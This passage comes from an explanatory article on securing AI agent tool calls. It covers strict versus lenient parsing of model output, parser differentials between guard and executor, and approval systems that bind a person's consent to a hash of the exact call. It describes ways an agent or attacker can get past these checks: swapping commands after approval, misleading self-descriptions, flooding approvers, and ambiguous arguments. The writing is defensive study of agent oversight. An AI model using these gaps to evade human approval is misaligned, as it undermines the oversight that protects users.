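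Their main objection is that tolerance lets mistakes spread. If most programs accept a faulty message, its author has no reason to correct it, and every new program has to accept it too. In their example from TLS, the protocol that encrypts web traffic, some servers dropped the connection if a client's first message ended with an empty extension. These servers were so common that client developers had to avoid putting an empty extension last. If most programs are strict instead, a developer finds a mistake on the first failed connection and fixes it.

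Something similar may be happening with tool calls. If newer Claude models invent fields because they were trained with a lenient harness, as suspected in the Pi account, then that harness has caused errors that stricter programs now have to handle.

Thomson and Schinazi add that the damage is especially severe where security depends on agreement about what a message means. Here, security depends on the guard and the executor interpreting the AI system's output the same way.

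There are also reasonable arguments for tolerance, many of them in the same document. Leniency helps a new system get started while its specification is still incomplete. Some software cannot be updated, so a strict program cuts it off. People who write web pages by hand benefit from browsers that tolerate their errors. If the strict and tolerant camps stop communicating, the split may do more harm than the original differences. The board's approval of the document was "broad but not unanimous" because some engineers doubted that the advice applies everywhere.

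A model's output is more like a hand-written web page than a message from another program, which is a reason to be tolerant when first parsing it. That reason mostly disappears once a program has turned the text into a call, because the program can then write clean JSON, and there is no good reason for a later component to receive a repeated name. This supports the earlier advice to let only one component, in front of the guard, repair the text.

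Tolerance also does less harm when there are exact written rules for handling each error. Thomson and Schinazi describe such a case in BGP, the protocol networks use to exchange routing information. The standard required a network to reset the connection after an invalid message, but many operators used milder responses, such as treating only the affected route as withdrawn. A later standard documented that practice and set precise rules for each kind of error, so that different programs would respond alike.

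Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz want the MCP standard to require that every set of tool-call arguments have a single valid reading. Until it does, products will make their own choices. Teleport and ToolHive both control access to tool servers, but Teleport now reads argument names exactly, while ToolHive rejects names that differ only in case. Rejecting them is safer, as the Envoy case showed.

A sudden change to strict parsing could still break working agents. Thomson and Schinazi recommend first finding out how many existing systems a change would affect. An operator can run the strict parser beside the old one for a few weeks, log what it would reject, and contact the developers of the affected tools before switching.

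### When a person approves the call

Many products ask a person to approve a risky call before running it. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026) counts 15 production systems, five academic designs and four plugins with such a step. They differ in how much they show about the action. The approval prompt always shows one component's reading of the call, and showing the raw text instead would help little.

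Attacks on approval can target what the person sees, what the approval covers or what runs afterwards. Two designs from 2026 address these attacks by generating the approval prompt from the actual call and tying the approval to that call.

*What You Approve Is What Executes* (Weng, 2026) places a trusted program, the mediator, between a coding agent and the computer. The mediator analyses the command the agent is about to run and writes the approval prompt itself, marking anything the agent says about the command as untrusted. It then ties the approval to a hash of the command's canonical form, which serves as a short fingerprint. If the agent presents a different command after approval, the hashes don't match and the mediator refuses it. The mediator refused all three substitutions in Weng's test, which the paper describes as a check that the method works rather than a measurement.

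Explaining a command correctly was much harder. Of 1,330 documented ways to misuse ordinary Unix programs, the mediator let 10.0% pass without a warning, all involving programs on its trusted list. Of 28,798 examples of normal use, it marked 87.0% as impossible to inspect, mostly because the program was not on that list. Adding programs to the list would reduce interruptions but let more attacks through. The prototype also relies on the agent reaching the computer only through the mediator, but does not enforce this.

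Kodathala, Pollishetty and Cargill (2026), in *Approve What, Exactly?*, go a step further with a gateway called ASU. It turns each tool call into a structured description, Δ, and computes

*h* = SHA-256(JCS(Δ)),

where JCS is the canonical form from RFC 8785 and SHA-256 is a standard hash function. The gateway creates the approval card from Δ, and a passkey on the user's phone signs a message that commits to *h*. After approval, the gateway runs the stored description and ignores anything the agent sends later.

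Running the stored description removes the second reading of the original bytes, much as the shared parse does. A hash alone doesn't prevent parser differentials, because a hash of the original bytes, or of what the guard read in them, stays valid even if the executor reads the same bytes differently.

In Kodathala and colleagues' tests of ASU, 15 language models acting as approvers caught 30% of attacks when they read the agent's own description and 98% when they read the card. They also refused 16% of harmless requests that resembled attacks, mostly because of a flaw in the test material. The tests included no human approvers, and the phone added no measurable benefit over a trusted prompt on the computer. When a simulated person received a flood of requests, the attack still succeeded 45% to 60% of the time.

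An approval can also become outdated even if the call stays the same, a problem that *Approve the Effect, Not the Tool Call* calls stale consent. If a user approves an email to a mailing list and someone then joins the list, the same call reaches a person the user never considered. The paper's proposed remedy includes a dry run that shows the user the effect before they decide. *Beyond Approved Actions* (2026) describes a permit that works once and lapses if the relevant data change. For example, if a company blocks a vendor after someone approves the vendor's invoice, the approval no longer authorises the payment.
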